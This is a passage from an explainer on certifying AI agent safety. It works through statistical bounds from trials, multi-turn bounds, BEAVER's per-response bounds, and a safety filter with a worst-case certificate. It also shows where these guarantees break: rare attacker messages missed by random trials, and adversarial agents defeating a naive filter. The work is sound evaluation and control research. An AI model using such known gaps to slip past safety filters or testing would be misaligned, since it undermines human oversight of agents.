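This correlation suggests that the check picks out better workflows. It doesn't show that passing the check caused the improvement, because the passing workflows also tended to have more precise instructions and better retry loops. With only six workflows per benchmark, such differences could matter a lot. A repair experiment comes closer to showing cause. In one failing workflow, the steps could not see the earlier conversation. After the researchers fixed this, GPT-5.2's score rose from 52% to 62% and GLM-5's from 48% to 60%. The missing information evidently mattered, although an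 engineer might have found the fault without Lean.

Neither result certifies an individual answer. Agents with passing workflows still failed on about 42% of the programming problems. A language model wrote the conditions that Lean checked. A manual review found that 36 of the 1,460 were wrong, but correcting them changed none of the verdicts.

### What a clean run of trials guarantees

Repeated trials can support a guarantee about outputs, but a statistical one. Suppose the shop draws 3,000 refund requests at random from its real traffic, asks each customer afterwards, and finds no wrong refund. If the true failure rate is *p* and the trials are independent, the chance of seeing no failures is (1 − *p*)³⁰⁰⁰. The 95% upper limit is the rate at which this chance falls to 5%:

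(1 − *p*)³⁰⁰⁰ = 0.05,  so  *p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/3000) ≈ 0.001.

The failure rate could therefore be as high as 0.1%, which at 1,000 tasks a day is about one wrong refund a day. After *n* trials with no failures, the upper limit on the failure rate is roughly 3/*n*. To show that failures happen less than once a year at that volume, the shop would need about 1.1 million trials with no failures. The limit also assumes that every failure is noticed. If customers report only half of the wrong refunds, it doubles from 0.1% to 0.2%.

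The calculation assumes that future requests come from the same mix as the trials. Suppose 30 of the 3,000 requests involved orders with two similar items. Even if all 30 succeeded, the failure rate for such orders could be as high as 9.5%. If a sale makes such orders half of the day's 1,000 tasks, there could be about 48 wrong refunds a day. The assumption also fails when someone attacks the agent. If one message in a million fools the agent, 3,000 random trials will almost certainly miss it, but an attacker who finds it can send it every time. A new model also needs new trials, whereas the proof of the daily limit holds for any model.

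The guarantee also depends on whether a trial is a single reply or a whole conversation. If each reply is safe with probability 0.99, multiplying the probabilities over 20 replies guarantees only an 82% chance that the whole conversation is safe. *Certified Multi-Turn Robustness for LLM Safety via Compositional Bounds and Safety Persistence* (2026) describes this exponential decline and looks for tighter bounds. Testers can avoid the multiplication by sampling whole conversations. One certification task in *Lumos* (2025) samples 1,000 three-turn conversations to bound, with 95% confidence, how often a model gives a harmful response. In another version, each question depends on the model's previous response. Each bound applies to conversations generated the same way as its samples, and a real attacker may use others.

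Another approach lets a model answer only when a confidence score is high enough, with the threshold set to keep errors below a target. *When Can Conformal Risk Control Certify LLM Outputs?* (2026) found that, when the target was strict, this rarely worked except for structured output. Under one calculation method, 47 of 51 successful certifications were for JSON, and almost none for question answering or classification.

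### Bounding one response

*BEAVER* (Wadhwa, Suresh and colleagues, 2025) bounds the probability that one model's response to one prompt passes an automatic check. The program uses the model's token probabilities to explore possible responses, starting with the most likely. It runs the check on each finished response and adds up the probabilities of those that pass and those that fail. If responses with a combined probability of 70% have passed, 5% have failed and 25% remain unexplored, the probability of passing is between 70% and 95%. Exploring more responses narrows the range, and the user can stop at any time with a valid result.

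This range has no sampling error, unlike a limit estimated from trials. Computing it requires access to the model's token probabilities and a check that always returns the same result for the same response. In tests for leaked personal data, insecure code and toxic text, the program identified up to 7.6 times as many risky prompts as a sampling method with the same budget. A claim about many prompts still requires a random sample of them.

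For "refund the kettle", the program might show that the agent chooses the $40 kettle at least 90% of the time, which would be good for Maya but not for Tom.

### Bounding any model behind a filter

Baheri and Wei's filter comes with a certificate, an upper limit on the probability that an agent reaches an unsafe state within a fixed number of steps. Engineers first describe the situation with a few yes-or-no facts, such as whether the agent has confirmation and whether it has deleted a protected file. They then use logs to estimate how each tool call changes those facts, with a margin for uncertainty.

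The calculation works backwards from the end of the task. Let *Vₖ*(*s*) be the worst-case risk with *k* steps left in state *s*. It is 1 in an unsafe state and 0 after a safe stop or, in any other state, when no steps remain. In every other case,

*Vₖ*(*s*) = the maximum, over permitted actions *a* and outcome probabilities *q* for *a* that fit the logs, of Σ *q*(*s*′)*Vₖ*₋₁(*s*′),

where the sum is over the possible next states *s*′. The filter forbids actions until the risk at the start is below a chosen ceiling. Because the maximum covers every permitted action, the result holds for any model, including one that follows an attacker's instructions. In the file-system tests, seven agents had no unsafe outcomes in 1,050 runs behind the filter. Without it, the worst agent caused harm in 84.7% of its runs.

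The certificate depends on several assumptions. The chosen facts and the action must contain everything relevant to what happens next, and the environment must respond the same way whichever model acts. Stopping must always be possible and safe, and unsafe states must be permanent. Engineers must also list every possible outcome of each call. The logs need to cover only normal operation, because the method treats an untried action as maximally uncertain. A simpler method that did not account for this uncertainty certified zero risk, yet an adversarial agent caused harm every time.

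The guarantee weakens if the chosen facts leave something out. If history missing from those facts can shift the outcome probabilities by a total of *η* at each step, the risk limit over *T* steps rises by up to *Tη*/2. With *η* = 0.01 and ten steps, the increase is up to five percentage points. The facts can include which item the customer selected, but not which one the customer meant.

### Combining probabilities between layers

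In May 2026, Bensalem, Dong and colleagues (2026), in *A Three-Layer Probabilistic Assume-Guarantee Architecture Is Structurally Required*, proposed a way to combine proofs and estimates. One layer checks that a plan fits the user's intent and the rules, another that conditions are ones for which the system is certified, and a third that execution stays safe. Each layer has a probabilistic contract, a promise that it will meet its guarantee with a stated probability if its assumptions hold. If those probabilities are *p*_U, *p*_O and *p*_F, then

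Pr(all three guarantees hold) ≥ *p*_U + *p*_O + *p*_F − 2.

This bound follows from adding the three chances of failure, which need not be independent. If the probabilities are 0.98, 0.999 and 0.999, the bound is 0.978. Even if proofs raised the last two to 1, the bound would rise only to 0.98, the probability that the plan is right. The shop would still have to estimate that probability by asking customers.

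Bensalem and colleagues illustrate their bounds with example numbers but have not measured them on a working agent. They acknowledge that the probabilities are hard to estimate, because each step of an agent's run depends on the earlier ones and the same instruction can produce different plans. Each new model requires estimates from new runs. Their bounds also don't cover usefulness, since a layer that blocks every action could still meet its guarantee.
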